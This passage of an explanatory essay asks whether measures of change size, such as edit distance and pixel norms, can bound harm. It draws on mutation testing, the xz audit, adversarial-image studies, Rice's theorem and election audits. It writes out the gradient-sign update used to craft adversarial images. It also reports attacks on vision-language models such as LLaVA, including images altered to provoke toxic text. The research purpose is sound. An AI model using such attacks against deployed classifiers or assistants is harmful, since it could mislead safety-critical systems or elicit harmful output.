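| 25% | 2 or fewer |
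| 50% | 4 or fewer |
| 75% | 9 or fewer |
| 95% | 22 or fewer |
| 100% | 54 or fewer |

Edit distance is the same in both directions when insertions and deletions count equally, so undoing a four-line repair is a four-line edit that brings the bug back. In one repair, the developers changed `!=` (not equal) to `==`. In another, they changed `p1` to `p2` in code that was meant to compare two shapes but compared the first with itself. In 118 cases the repair only added lines, so deleting those lines would restore the bug. The added lines were often a missing guard, such as a check that a position is not past the end of a text.

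Defects4J omits unrelated changes, including refactoring, from its repairs, so the original updates may have been longer. It also leaves out repairs to build scripts and configuration files, which excludes faults like the one in xz. Since every entry is a bug, the collection can't show how many four-line edits are harmless, or whether longer edits are riskier on average.

### Faults made on purpose

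Programmers use mutation testing to find out how good their tests are. A tool makes many copies of a program, called mutants, each with one small change, such as `>` to `>=` or `+` to `-`, and runs the program's tests on each one. A mutant is "killed" if any test fails. If every test passes, the tests may have a gap.

Suppose the dose function has two tests, both with a limit of 10. A dose of 5 should give True, and a dose of 50 should give False. The table shows what four mutants return.

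| Change | Dose of 5 | Dose of 50 | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| `>` to `<` | False | True | Killed |
| `>` to `>=` | True | False | Survives |
| `False` to `True` | True | True | Killed |
| `True` to `False` | False | False | Killed |

The surviving mutant rejects a dose of exactly 10, which the original program allows. A test with that dose catches it. CrowdStrike's tests had a similar gap. All twelve automated test cases used a wildcard in the 21st field, so they passed even though the software supplied only 20 values.

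Some mutants survive every possible test because the edit has no effect. This function finds the largest number in a list:

```python
def largest(numbers):
    best = numbers[0]
    for n in numbers:
        if n > best:
            best = n
    return best
```

Changing `>` to `>=` here makes the function sometimes replace the best number so far with an equal one, but for whole numbers the answer is always the same. Programmers call the changed version an equivalent mutant. The same one-character edit changed what the dose function did, so you can't judge whether an edit matters by its size or by the characters involved.

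Equivalent mutants make the results of mutation testing harder to read. The usual score is

killed mutants / (all mutants − equivalent mutants)

Calculating it exactly requires working out which survivors are equivalent, and no program can do that in every case. Researchers also use planted faults to test language models. Zhu and colleagues, for example, use one-token bugs to study over-editing, which means changing more of a program than the task requires.

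### Large changes that leave a program's behaviour alone

Programmers often make large edits that aren't supposed to affect what a program does. Reformatting a file can alter every line without changing any instructions. Renaming a variable that appears 200 times takes 200 token edits. Standard edit distance has no operation for moving text, so moving a 50-line function can count as 50 deletions and 50 insertions. Refactoring, which reorganises code while keeping its behaviour the same, can involve all of these.

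Such changes are harmless only if the programmer makes them throughout the program. The rewritten dose function calls its second input `maximum` instead of `limit`, so any call that still uses the old name, such as `all_safe(doses, limit=10)`, will now fail.

After the backdoor was discovered, Collin audited Jia Tan's contributions one by one. He approved many large changes, including moved code, reordered lines and a series of edits that replaced one style of quotation mark with another. To check the quotation marks, Collin gives a command that makes the same replacement in the old text and lists any lines that still differ. He also notes that an edit to spacing "really is just space change, no dots."

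Refactoring was harder to check. In early 2023, Jia Tan tidied up some duplicated code and introduced a bug. Collin noticed it, and the two of them fixed it that November. The audit doesn't treat this as sabotage.

Two large changes to the part of xz that decompresses files also passed, after Collin corrected one number. To save time, the new code checked that enough input remained once per pass through a loop, instead of before every byte. Jia Tan's version required 20 bytes, but a pass could need 21, so Collin raised the number to 21. Collin's next change moved a step out of the loop, so 20 bytes were then enough.

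## What did adversarial images show about pixel norms?

A change to a picture can do harm even when it is too small for people to see. Suppose a car recognises road signs with a classifier, a program that sorts images into categories. If an attacker alters the image of a stop sign very slightly, a person still sees a stop sign, but the classifier can label it as something else, so the car drives on.

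In studies of such attacks, the usual limit on the change is an L∞ norm of 8/255. Digital images commonly store each colour value as a whole number from 0 to 255, so this allows a change of eight steps, about 3% of the range. To find a damaging change δ, an attacker who knows the network's internals can repeat one update:

δ ← clip(δ + α · sign(∇L), −ε, ε)

Here L is the network's error on the altered image, and the sign of its gradient ∇L shows whether raising or lowering each value would increase that error. The attacker moves every value by a small step α, such as 2/255, in the direction that increases the error, then reduces any total change larger than the limit ε to ε. Thousands of these small changes together push the network towards the same mistake.

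The most common defence, adversarial training, runs this attack on the training images and trains the network to give the altered images their original labels. This assumes that every image within the limit still shows what the original showed.

### Altered images that mislead people

Sharif and colleagues tested that assumption on 399 people, who each labelled 25 images from a choice of ten categories. Some saw unaltered images, some saw images altered to fool only a network, and the rest saw images altered to fool people as well. The L0 test used handwritten digits from the MNIST dataset, and the other two tests used CIFAR-10, a set of small colour photographs of animals and vehicles. The table shows how often people chose the original label.

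| Norm | Size of change | Unaltered | Altered to fool a network | Altered to fool people too |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| L0 | about 4.5% of pixels | 95% | 97% | 3% |
| L2 | 6 | 93% | 89% | 57% |
| L∞ | 0.1 | 91% | 79% | 36% |

A member of the team made the misleading digits by hand in a photo editor, changing about 35 of the 784 pixels on average. For the photographs, a program searched for changes of the permitted size that fooled the network. It either started from versions that looked unlike the original or steered towards them.

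The results were clearest for the digits. By majority vote, none of the altered digits kept its original label, and people were nearly as confident as with the unaltered ones (4.19 out of 5, against 4.47). Confidence fell to about 3 for the misleading photographs, so many of them had probably become unclear without coming to look like something else.

The limits for photographs were also large. An L∞ norm of 0.1 is about three times 8/255. Sharif and colleagues chose the L2 limit of 6 themselves because they found no published threshold below which people can't see a change. Their limit is twelve times the 0.5 that a leading robustness ranking now uses. Their results therefore don't show whether smaller changes to photographs can mislead people.

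Small rotations and shifts show the opposite problem, because they can produce a large L2 distance while leaving a photograph recognisable. The altered dog and horse photographs described earlier were at least 15.83 from the originals and still recognisable, yet a network labelled the dog a cat and the horse a truck. When photographs were altered by an L2 distance of 6 to mislead people, people misread 43% of them. An L2 threshold high enough to allow the recognisable dog would also allow those photographs. Networks trained to resist norm-bounded attacks also failed on rotated and shifted images, which lie far outside the limits used in training.

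A different norm might match human vision better. Sen, Zhu and colleagues (2019), in *Should Adversarial Attacks Use Pixel p-Norm?*, looked for one by asking people to strengthen a change until they could just notice it. In two versions of a cat photograph, the change affected 288 colour values, each by the same amount a. The Lp norm of such a change is

a × 288^(1/p)

wherever the affected pixels are. But the 42 participants typically noticed the change at a = 37 when the pixels were around the cat's eyes, and only at a = 62 when they were scattered. No choice of p can account for that difference. The norm with p = 3 came closest to people's judgments overall, and it isn't one of the usual three.

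Sen and colleagues also looked at why other researchers used pixel norms. Of the 32 papers they surveyed, 27 used them. About half of those followed earlier papers, and a fifth assumed without evidence that norms match human perception.

### New digits that keep their old labels

Most research on adversarial examples looks for changes that a network reacts to and people don't. In *Fundamental Tradeoffs between Invariance and Sensitivity to Adversarial Perturbations*, Tramèr, Behrmann and colleagues (2020) looked for changes that people react to and a network doesn't. In one of their examples, changing 20 pixels turns a handwritten 3 into a 5, but some networks still label it a 3.

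To alter an 8, their program searches the training images of other digits for the one that differs from the 8 in the fewest pixels, allowing slight rotations, shifts and stretches. If it finds a 3, for example, it groups the differing pixels into patches and copies only the patches that make the 8 look like a 3. Under L∞, it instead blends the original towards the other digit, changing each pixel by at most 0.3 or 0.4. One of the researchers also altered 50 digits by hand.

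Forty people then labelled the images. An alteration counted as successful if at least 70% of those who saw it agreed on a new digit.

| Alteration | Successful |
|---|---|
| L0, automated (about 26 pixels) | 55% |
| L∞ of 0.3, automated | 21% |
| L∞ of 0.4, automated | 37% |
| L∞ of 0.4, by hand | 88% |

Tramèr and colleagues tested one network with a mathematical proof that, for at least 87% of the test images, no change within an L∞ norm of 0.4 could make it give a label other than the original. On the 100 automated images at that limit, the network gave the original label 96% of the time. It agreed with people on about 60% of those images (the paper gives both 60% and 63%) and on only 12% of the hand-made ones. A program that always repeated the original label would agree with people about as often, since people saw a new digit in 37% of the automated images and 88% of the hand-made ones.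 These results are consistent with the proof, which covered only the network's answer.

Networks without any defence did better. The next table shows how often each network agreed with people on images in which people saw a new digit.

| Network | L0 | L∞ of 0.3 | L∞ of 0.4 |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 80% | 33% | 51% |
| Adversarially trained at L∞ 0.3 | 56% | 0% | 16% |
| Binary-ABS, which rounds pixels to black or white | 47% | 0% | 8% |

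These are small samples, with only 21 images in the middle column. An earlier version of the experiment, in *Exploiting Excessive Invariance Caused by Norm-Bounded Adversarial Robustness* (Jacobsen, Behrmann and colleagues, 2019), used an undefended network that got only 54% of the L0 images right and none of the L∞ ones. The size of an undefended network's advantage therefore seems to depend on which network researchers pick.

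A defence such as rounding can make a network worse. If a network first rounds every pixel to black or white, raising a black pixel from 0 to 0.4 does not change its answer, which makes it very robust under L∞. But a person can see a grey stroke of that brightness, and adding one can turn a 1 into a 4. The two images are identical after rounding, so the network cannot tell them apart.

Adversarial training can have a similar effect. If the limit is wide enough to include a 5 that lies close to a 3, the network learns to call that 5 a 3, and a wider limit includes more such images. Tramèr and colleagues trained a series of networks with L∞ limits from 0 to 0.4. The wider the limit, the less often the networks' labels for the altered digits matched people's labels. Even networks trained with limits below 0.1 matched them less often than an undefended network did. Jacobsen and colleagues describe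 the extreme case, a classifier that gives every image the same label. It is useless, even though it is perfectly robust because no change to an image can alter its label.

The problem doesn't show up in ordinary tests because MNIST's digits are tidy and centred, and few fall between two classes. A network can score well using crude clues, such as the number of bright pixels, which predicts an 8 fairly well in MNIST but would be a poor guide to handwriting in general. Training on rotated and shifted digits brought networks closer to people's judgments, but those also trained to resist large pixel changes still did worse than the undefended network.

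A narrower limit avoids some of these errors, but the network can still fail on harmless changes that exceed it. In an example from Jacobsen and colleagues, adding nearly invisible noise to a photograph of a tennis ball produces an L2 distance of 24.3, while replacing the ball with a strawberry produces 23.2. A network robust to all changes as large as the noise would have to give the strawberry photograph the same label as the tennis ball.

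### How well do people do at the standard limit?

The limits in the digit experiments were about ten times the standard limit for photographs, 8/255, or more, so the results may not apply to that smaller limit. In *Adversarial Robustness Limits via Scaling-Law and Human-Alignment Studies*, Bartoldson, Diffenderfer and colleagues (2024) found that the standard limit is mostly safe. They trained many networks of different sizes on CIFAR-10 photographs and similar synthetic ones. The best network labelled 73.71% of the test images correctly under AutoAttack, a standard set of four attacks. They predicted from the trend across networks that this accuracy would level off at around 90%, however much computing power anyone used.

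To see whether people would do better, three members of the team labelled the altered versions of the 2,629 images, out of 10,000, that the best network got wrong. Their average accuracy on the full set would be 90.46%, assuming they would have labelled the other 7,371 correctly, which works out at about 64% on the images they saw. They were about 25% less accurate on these than on the same photographs before the attack, so the alterations caused most of their mistakes, but not all.

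The researchers judged that 727 of the images, about 7% of the full test set, no longer matched their labels. On 39% of those, most of the people made the same mistake as the network. Removing all 727 raises the network's score to 79.49% and the estimated human score to 96.46%.

The estimate of human performance relies on only three labellers, all from the research team, and nobody checked the other 7,371 images. If some of those would also mislead people, the true figure is below 90%. The figure also depends on the network under attack. Earlier work that Bartoldson and colleagues cite found that images made to fool a robust network are more likely to mislead people than images made to fool an ordinary one. An ordinary network usually fails after a meaningless change, so an attacker has little reason to make a horse look like something else.

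Fort (2025) reports informal evidence of the same effect in *A Note on Implementation Errors in Recent Adaptive Attacks Against Multi-Resolution Self-Ensembles*. Fort showed a lecture audience two altered photographs. Changes of at most 8/255 had led a robust network to label a house as a road and the sea as a mountain. Given a short list of options, most of the audience agreed with the network.

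People can also notice a change without misreading the image. In *An h-space Based Adversarial Attack for Protection Against Few-shot Personalization* (2025), 26 volunteers compared altered portraits with the originals side by side and did no better than chance at picking out the altered one when the limit was 4/255. *Vision-Language Model Confidence Is Not a Property of the Answer* (2026) reports that at a limit of 8/255, a minority of altered images look different on close inspection.

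Adversarial images made under the same pixel limit can look altered to very different degrees, depending on the attack. In *Pushing the Frontier of Black-Box LVLM Attacks via Fine-Grained Detail Targeting* (2026), ten people looked at 40 images, each made by one of four attacks, and each person picked the 20 that looked most altered. All four attacks had an L∞ limit of 16/255, meaning they could change no pixel value by more than that amount. People picked 84% of the images from one attack but only about 30% of those from each of two others.

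### Norm bounds as a minimum test

Researchers can reasonably defend using norm bounds. In *Position*, Rando, Zhang and colleagues (2025) describe robustness within a bound as necessary but not sufficient for robustness in general. Without some limit, an attacker could replace a photograph of a cat with one of a dog and count the new label as a success. Some critics of norm bounds also defend them. Carlini and Tramèr, who worked on the digit experiments, were part of the *Position* team, and Jacobsen and colleagues call norm robustness "a useful benchmark task".

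An exact limit also makes research easier to check. *Adversarial Alignment for LLMs Requires Simpler, Reproducible, and More Measurable Objectives* (2025) recounts how researchers broke more than 50 published defences, and how public rankings with fixed attack settings then made results comparable. In a recent example from Fort's note, a team reported reducing a defence's accuracy to nearly zero. But their program started each round of the attack from the previous round's altered image, so the changes added up to as much as 160/255, twenty times the limit. When Fort kept to the limit, a stronger version of the defence kept its accuracy above 20%. The error would have been harder to prove under a vaguer rule, such as "changes that look small".

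A network that mislabels a photograph after a change people can't see isn't robust, so passing the test is necessary when the limit is small enough. But it is necessary only if the images within the limit keep their original meaning. At a limit of 8/255 on CIFAR-10, Bartoldson and colleagues' figures suggest that roughly one image in fourteen loses its original meaning when the attack targets a very robust network. At 0.4 on handwritten digits, this happens so often that a network has to disagree with people to get a high score.

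Using the bound for training is riskier than using it for testing. A few invalid images in a test make a network's score slightly too low, but training on such images teaches the network to ignore changes that matter.

It is also unclear how far robustness to small-norm changes carries over to other changes. *Beyond Standard Benchmarks* (2026) tested versions of CLIP, a widely used model that matches images with text, on natural variations in images. The versions trained for robustness did worse than ordinary CLIP in most cases. *A New Kind of Adversarial Example* (2026) studies large changes that make an image unrecognisable to people but leave the model's label the same, the reverse of the usual attack. It raises the open question of whether robustness to small changes carries over to these large ones.

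Language models have no comparable test. Rando and colleagues explain that a norm bound makes sense for a classifier because the right answer depends on the original image. A chatbot shouldn't give harmful instructions no matter what the user types, so there is no original input to stay close to. They suggest that researchers who want to advance scientific understanding should find similarly well-defined problems for language models.

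### Robustness in 2025 and 2026

Image classifiers are still far from robust, even within the standard limits. In *VanillaBench*, Bunzel (2026) reviewed 186 networks from the public ranking RobustBench. The most robust one on CIFAR-10 at 8/255 labels 75.28% of images correctly under attack. Bartoldson and colleagues estimate that people would label about 90% correctly. If so, images that no longer match their labels can't explain most of the network's errors.

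Robust networks are also less accurate on unaltered images. That network gets 93.6% of them right, while the best ordinary network gets 99.5%. Some of the difference comes from the networks' different designs. When Bunzel compared robust networks with ordinary ones of the same or a similar design, the average drop in accuracy ranged from 3.5 percentage points on one of the four tests to 17.5 on another.

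Researchers now apply the same limits to vision-language models, which answer questions about images. In *Investigating Adversarial Robustness of Multi-modal Large Language Models*, Malik, Naseer and Khan (2026) attacked LLaVA, an open model that uses CLIP to process images. The table shows its average accuracy on four sets of questions, with and without their strongest attack at 8/255.

| Version of LLaVA | Unaltered images | Under attack |
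|---|---|---|
| Ordinary CLIP | 54.5% | 0% |
| Ordinary CLIP, with adversarial training of LLaVA | 36.5% | 0% |
| Robust CLIP | 51.9% | 25.9% |
| Robust CLIP, with adversarial training of LLaVA | 49.4% | 30.2% |

Adversarial training helped only when the part of the model that processes images was already robust. The robust versions also produced much less toxic text when the researchers altered images to provoke it, so the benefit here went beyond reducing wrong answers.

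A simpler defence was to add random noise to each image before the model processed it. This raised the ordinary version's performance under attack from near zero to about the level of the robust ones, even when the attacker expected noise but didn't know the exact noise that would be added. Malik and colleagues warn that the noise doesn't protect against an attacker with full knowledge of the defence.

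Some newer papers report much larger gains from their defences. In *Closed-Loop Bidirectional Prompting for Adversarial Robustness of Vision Language Models* (2026), ordinary CLIP correctly labels 59.69% of images from ImageNet, a large collection of photographs, but only 1.15% under attack. The new method raises accuracy under attack to 58.42%. That figure may fall, because many earlier defences failed once somebody designed an attack specifically for them.

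Pixel norms remain common in this work. *Dual Adversarial Fine-tuning for Enhancing Robustness of Large Vision Language Model* (2026), for example, reports results at an L∞ limit of 2/255. Other researchers study edits that a pixel norm describes badly, and use human judgments to check the limits they set on those edits. In *StyleAT* (2026), a study of how to defend face recognition against edits that alter a person's appearance, 181 people judged whether pairs of photographs showed the same person. Their accuracy fell steadily as the limits on the edits rose.

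## Could any distance between inputs track meaning or harm?

Edit distance and pixel norms are crude measures, so their failures leave open whether someone could design a better one. Tramèr and colleagues, who ran the experiments on altered digits, define what a better distance would have to do. Tramèr and colleagues assume a labelling oracle O, an idealised judge that gives the true label of any input. A distance is *aligned* with the oracle if, for every input x, all inputs with the same label as x are closer to it than any input with a different label:

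O(x₁) = O(x) and O(x₂) ≠ O(x) ⇒ dist(x, x₁) < dist(x, x₂)

If even one set of three inputs breaks this rule, the distance and the oracle are misaligned. Tramèr and colleagues call this distance-oracle misalignment.

Word distance does not satisfy alignment for the drug sentences. Let x be "Do not give the drug", x₁ "The drug must be withheld" and x₂ "Do give the drug", and let the label be what a nurse should do. Then x and x₁ have the label "withhold", and x₂ has the label "give". Alignment requires x₁ to be closer to x than x₂ is, but the word distance from x is 5 for x₁ and 1 for x₂. Dividing by length does not correct the order.

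When distance is misaligned with meaning or harm, a limit on change size can't allow every harmless change and also exclude every harmful one. In the drug sentences, any limit that allows the harmless paraphrase also allows the reversal.

The same dilemma affects training, as it did with the handwritten digits. Let ε* be the size of the smallest change that gives x a different true label. Training with a limit below ε* leaves the model vulnerable to larger changes that don't alter the true label, while training with a limit above ε* teaches it some wrong labels.

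### Why an aligned distance is as hard as the task itself

Tramèr and colleagues prove that building an aligned distance is as hard as building a perfect classifier. Suppose someone has an aligned distance and one labelled example of each class. Take a new input q, and let y be its true label. Let a be the example with label y, and b any of the other examples. Since a has the same label as q and b does not, alignment gives

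dist(q, a) < dist(q, b)

This holds for every choice of b, so a is the nearest example to q. A nearest-neighbour classifier, which copies the label of the nearest example, would therefore always be right.

An aligned distance would need only two examples, "Give the drug" and "Withhold the drug", to correctly sort every instruction to give or withhold the drug, however oddly worded. Edit distance missorts "Do not give the drug" because that sentence is two word edits from "Give the drug" and three from "Withhold the drug".

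Conversely, a perfect classifier provides an aligned distance, which is 0 if the classifier gives two inputs the same label and 1 if it doesn't. So a developer with an aligned distance for harm would already have a perfect detector of harmful texts, and could run it on the edited text without measuring the edit.

### What the proof leaves open

The proof is a reduction, so it shows that one problem is as hard as another, not that either is impossible. When a task is easy, an aligned distance is easy to build too. For example, if the label is whether a text contains the word "drug", a few lines of code are enough. As language models get better at judging meaning, people can use them to build better distances.

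Alignment is also a very strict requirement, because every photograph of a cat has to be closer to a given cat photograph than any photograph of a dog is. Limiting the size of changes requires only that inputs very close to the original keep its label. This is realistic for photographs, since a pixel can change by a tiny amount, and most images keep their meaning at the standard limit of 8/255. In text, the smallest possible edit replaces, adds or removes a whole symbol, which may reverse the meaning.

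A distance that is usually right may also be easier to build than a perfect one. In *Balanced Adversarial Training*, Chen, Ji and Evans (2022) attacked BERT and RoBERTa, two older language models, on the task of judging whether one sentence follows from another. Their synonym attack replaces any number of words with near-synonyms, which usually leaves the right answer unchanged, and succeeds if the model changes its answer. Their antonym attack replaces one word with its opposite, which usually changes the right answer, and succeeds if the model keeps its old answer. The harmless edits could therefore be much larger than the edits that changed the meaning.

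Training the models on sentences with synonyms swapped in protected them against the synonym attack but made the antonym attack more successful. Chen and colleagues then tried a method they call balanced training, which adds a penalty based on d, the distance between two sentences in the model's internal numbers:

α · d(x, synonym version) + β · max(0, m − d(x, antonym version))

The first term pulls a sentence and its synonym version together. The second pushes the antonym version away until it is at least m from the original. The weights α and β set how much each term counts. The table shows how often the attacks succeeded.

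| Model and training | Synonym attack | Antonym attack |
|---|---|---|
| BERT, ordinary | 37% | 57% |
| BERT, synonyms only | 11% | 63% |
| BERT, balanced | 27% | 35% |
| RoBERTa, ordinary | 31% | 56% |
| RoBERTa, synonyms only | 10% | 67% |
| RoBERTa, balanced | 27% | 39% |

Balanced training protected against both attacks better than ordinary training did, and accuracy on unaltered sentences hardly changed. But it lost more than half of the protection that synonym training had provided. The tests also used the same kinds of swap as the training, so they don't show whether the learned distance would reflect a dropped "not" or a moved decimal point. And some antonym swaps don't change the right answer, so a model hasn't made a mistake by keeping its answer in those cases.

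There is similar evidence for images. *Scaling Adversarial Training to Large Perturbation Bounds* (2022) describes an attack that makes large changes to a picture, with a penalty based on LPIPS, a learned measure of how different two pictures look. With a low penalty, the attack tends to change what the picture shows. As the penalty rises, it shifts to changes that don't change the true label.

### Why no algorithm can compare every pair of programs

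For programs, computing a distance that tracks behaviour is provably impossible in general. The distance would have to be zero when two programs do the same thing on every input and above zero otherwise, and no algorithm can decide which is the case for every pair of programs.

This follows from Rice's theorem (1953), which the Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *Recursive Functions* states and proves. If a property depends only on what a program computes, and some programs have it while others don't, then no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether it has that property.

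No algorithm can decide, for every pair of programs, whether the two behave the same. If one could, it could also decide whether any given program returns 0 for every input, by comparing that program with one that always returns 0. Rice's theorem rules this out, because some programs return 0 for every input and others don't. The lecture notes *Elementary Recursive Function Theory* list the undecidability of whether two programs compute the same function among the theorem's consequences.

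The difficulty comes from programs that may never finish. Here are two versions of a function:

```python
def f(n):
    a(i)
    return 0
```

```python
def f(n):
    return 0
```

Suppose `a` is another function in the same file that only does a calculation, and `i` is a fixed input. If `a(i)` finishes, both versions return 0 for every `n`. If it runs forever, the first version never returns. An algorithm that could determine whether the two versions behave the same could therefore determine whether `a(i)` finishes.

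Turing showed in 1937 that no algorithm can determine in every case whether a program will finish. If one could, it could be used to write a program that reads another program's text and checks whether that program would finish when given its own text. The new program then runs forever if the other would finish, and finishes if it wouldn't. Given its own text, the new program would finish if and only if it didn't finish, which is a contradiction.

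The two versions of `f` differ by one line of four tokens. So no general method can decide whether even an edit that small changes what a program does. This is also why no tool can find every equivalent mutant.

But Rice's theorem only rules out an algorithm that is right about every program. Many pairs of programs are easy to compare. A function that takes two one-byte numbers has only 65,536 possible inputs, so if both versions always finish, a computer can run them on every input and compare the results.

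Restricting the language also makes it easier to check whether programs are equivalent. According to *Faultless* (2026), a study of tools that reconstruct source code from compiled programs, repetition through loops or recursion makes the general problem undecidable. *Peregrine* (2026) describes a language for processing network traffic that can't express every possible computation. Its checker turns two programs into formulas and uses a solver to search for values that make them differ. If no such values exist, the programs are equivalent.

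For general-purpose code, checkers often limit what they try to prove. Alive2 tests changes made by LLVM, a widely used set of compiler tools. It handles numbers of a fixed size and follows loops for a set number of passes, so it can miss a difference that appears on a later pass. In *LLVM Translation Validation Automated with Large Language Models and Lean*, Liao, Xu and colleagues (2026) removed some of these limits by having a language model write either a proof or a counterexample, which the proof checker Lean then verified. In their test, the system proved all 74 valid changes correct and refuted 73 of the 74 invalid ones. The loops in the test came from a restricted class.

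Another approach ignores what the individual statements do and compares only the order in which they run. Kappé (2025), in *On Propositional Program Equivalence (extended abstract)*, explains that this makes program equivalence decidable and practical to check. The method can help show that a program with three loops does the same as a version that merges them into one. But it can't show that `x = 1` and `y = 2` can safely swap places, because that depends on what the statements do.

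These limits exclude a lot of ordinary software. *IRONPROOF* (2026) describes a checker for programs translated from COBOL, an old business language, into Python. The checker could accept only 782 of 2,345 programs, and it proved 606 of those equivalent to their translations. The researchers had generated or written about three quarters of those 606 themselves. Most COBOL from other sources used files, loops or text operations that the checker couldn't handle.

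### Why a repair and its reversal have the same size

Even a perfect distance for meaning would be a poor measure of harm, because the distance from x to x′ is normally the same as the distance from x′ to x. *Principles of Lipschitz continuity in neural networks* (2026) notes that Levenshtein distance satisfies all the axioms of a metric, which include this symmetry. Removing the two-line Linux backdoor is therefore exactly as large a change as adding it, although only adding it does harm. Likewise, undoing a Defects4J repair is as large a change as making it.

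Let B(x) be how bad the outcome is when people use version x. The harm done by changing x to x′ is

B(x′) − B(x)

and the harm done by changing it back is the same number with the opposite sign. A formula based only on a symmetric distance gives the same number in both directions. It can be right both times only if that number is 0, which means the change made nobody better or worse off.

Weighting insertions and deletions differently makes edit distance asymmetric, but the distance still doesn't track harm. If deletions count for more than insertions, removing a safety check is a larger change than adding one, but adding a backdoor is a smaller change than removing it.

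Compiler developers handle the problem with a one-way test called refinement, which Liao and colleagues use. Roughly, the new version of the code must give the same result wherever the old one had a well-defined result. The new version may do anything where the old one had no defined behaviour, such as after a division by zero. Changing code to return 0 instead of dividing by zero passes the test, but the reverse change fails.

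### Why the same edit can be harmless or disastrous

The effect of an edit also depends on where it is. These two lines could come from a program that checks doses:

```python
# reject any dose > limit
if dose > limit:
```

The first line is a comment, which the computer ignores. Changing `>` to `<` there might mislead the next programmer, but it would not affect how the program runs. In the second line, the same one-character edit makes the program approve overdoses. Zhu and colleagues' measure of code edits would not count the change to the comment, because it strips comments out first. But it would give the same score to a changed condition in a safety check as to a changed condition that sets the colour of a button.

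A distance could take the surrounding code into account, but sometimes the whole text is the same and only the situation differs. Deleting "not" from the drug instruction can kill one patient and correct a typing mistake for another. Any distance calculated from the texts alone gives both cases the same score. Telling them apart would require the patient's record as well.

Learned measures of image similarity, such as LPIPS, have the same limitation. *Rethinking Communication Metrics* (2026) discusses systems that transmit a picture's content and rebuild the picture at the other end. A rebuilt picture can score well on LPIPS and still be useless for a task if it distorts one small detail that the task depends on. For example, the colour of a distant traffic light matters to a self-driving car but probably not to someone counting pedestrians.

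*The Many Senses of Visual Similarity* (2026) describes a method that lets users say in words which kind of similarity they want. In one example, two photographs of cars are alike in colour and camera distance but differ in the direction the cars face and the style of their roofs. A single overall score cannot show how similar the photographs are in each of these respects.

### How much choice does a size limit leave?

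A tight size limit can still allow a huge number of results. Take a text of 1,000 tokens in a language model's vocabulary of 100,000. To substitute one token, an editor picks one of 1,000 positions and one of 99,999 other tokens, which gives about 10⁸ possible results. With k substitutions, the number is

(ways to choose k of the 1,000 positions) × 99,999ᵏ

There are 499,500 ways to choose two positions, so two substitutions can produce about 5 × 10¹⁵ texts. The last column of the table shows how long a program would take to check them all at a million texts per second.

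| Substitutions | Possible results | Time to check them all |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 10⁸ | 100 seconds |
| 2 | 5 × 10¹⁵ | about 160 years |
| 3 | 1.7 × 10²³ | about 5 billion years |

Insertions and deletions would add more texts. Most of these texts are nonsense, and the count alone doesn't show that any are harmful. But if one in a billion of the texts with two substitutions were harmful, there would be about five million for an attacker to find, even though someone making two random typing errors would almost never produce one. An automated search for high-scoring edits could also find a harmful text if that text happened to score highly.

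### When does a size limit bound harm?

A limit on size does limit harm if each unit of change can do only a known amount of harm. Let H(x) be the harm that results from using version x, and suppose that for every pair of versions

H(x′) − H(x) ≤ L · d(x, x′)

If harm rises by at most L per unit of distance, a change of size ε adds at most L × ε to the harm. Mathematicians call L a Lipschitz constant. For text, some value of L nearly always exists, because a single edit can't do more harm than the worst possible outcome. But if one edit can cause that outcome, L is so large that the bound is useless. L must be known, and L × ε must be low compared with the harm that people are willing to risk.

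Elections meet this condition. *Limiting Risk by Turning Manifest Phantoms into Evil Zombies* (2012), a paper on auditing votes, explains that misreading one ballot can change the margin between two candidates by at most two votes. If the candidate with the most votes wins, and the leader is ahead by 1,000, 499 misread ballots can't change the winner. *Assessing the accuracy of the Australian Senate count* (2022) notes that the number needed to change the winner is half the gap between the top two.

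Auditors have used such ceilings in practice. *Implementing Risk-Limiting Post-Election Audits in California* (2009) describes an audit that left some ballots out of its sample. The auditors calculated that errors could have inflated the margin by at most 191 votes in the provisional ballots and at most 4 in one excluded precinct. They subtracted these 195 votes from the margin, which left 103. They then sampled the other 16 batches of ballots to check whether errors there had changed the result. This limited the risk of accepting a wrong outcome to 25% without a full hand count.

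The ceiling depends on the voting system. In Australian Senate elections, voters rank the candidates and officials count the ballots in rounds, so a few ballots can affect who drops out early and then who wins. *Auditing Australian Senate Ballots* (2016) describes a program that looks for small sets of ballots that would change the result if altered, though it may miss the smallest one. In Tasmania in 2016, the final margin was 71 out of 339,159 votes. The ceiling also applies only to changes in ballots, since changing one character in the counting software could alter every vote.

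Differential privacy limits by design how much a change in the data can affect published results. Software adds random noise to published statistics so that changing one person's record can change the probability of any result by at most a fixed factor, such as 1.1. Changing ten records can then change it by a factor of at most 1.1¹⁰, or about 2.6. If an insurer uses the published figures to decide which customers to refuse, one person's record can raise their own chance of refusal by a factor of at most 1.1. The US standards agency NIST says that the Census Bureau and large technology companies have used the method successfully, but that a lack of standards makes it hard to use well. NIST has published guidelines for evaluating vendors' claims.

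Engineers who tune machines can sometimes also limit how much a change of a given size could reduce safety, because many physical quantities change gradually. *On Safety in Safe Bayesian Optimization* (2024) describes the usual assumptions that at least one setting is known to be safe and that the safety score changes by at most L per unit of distance. If the current setting scores 10, the minimum safe score is 4, and L is 2, any setting within 3 units is safe to try. But if L is actually 3, moving 3 units could lower the score to 1.

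*Safe Guaranteed Exploration for Non-linear Systems* (2024) says that engineers know the constant in many cases. But *Safe Exploration in Finite Markov Decision Processes with Gaussian Processes* (2016) points out that safety can't be guaranteed without some prior knowledge of how it varies, for instance because it might jump suddenly. Such jumps are common in text and code.

Researchers have built text classifiers whose scores can change only by a limited amount with each character edit. In *Certified Robustness Under Bounded Levenshtein Distance*, Abad Rocamora, Chrysos and Cevher (2025) could prove that their classifier labels 38.80% of a set of news items correctly after any single edit, and 13.93% after any two. But, like the proofs for images, this limit applies only to the classifier's output and doesn't measure harm.

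A limit on the size of a change can sometimes prevent harm if the change is measured in a different unit. Changing "Inject 1.25 mg of morphine" to "Inject 12.5 mg of morphine" raises the dose by 11.25 mg, but a rule that no edit may change more than one word would allow it. If doctors know that an extra 0.5 mg is safe for a patient, a rule that no edit may raise the dose by more than 0.5 mg prevents an overdose.

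## Are larger changes riskier on average?

The Linux backdoor and similar cases show that a small edit can do great harm, but not how often small edits do. A developer who limits the size of changes may be relying on any of three claims: that larger changes cause accidental faults more often, that those faults are more serious, or that a limit restrains someone who is looking for a harmful change. Studies of software give good support to the first claim but very little to the other two.

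### Faulty patches in Firefox

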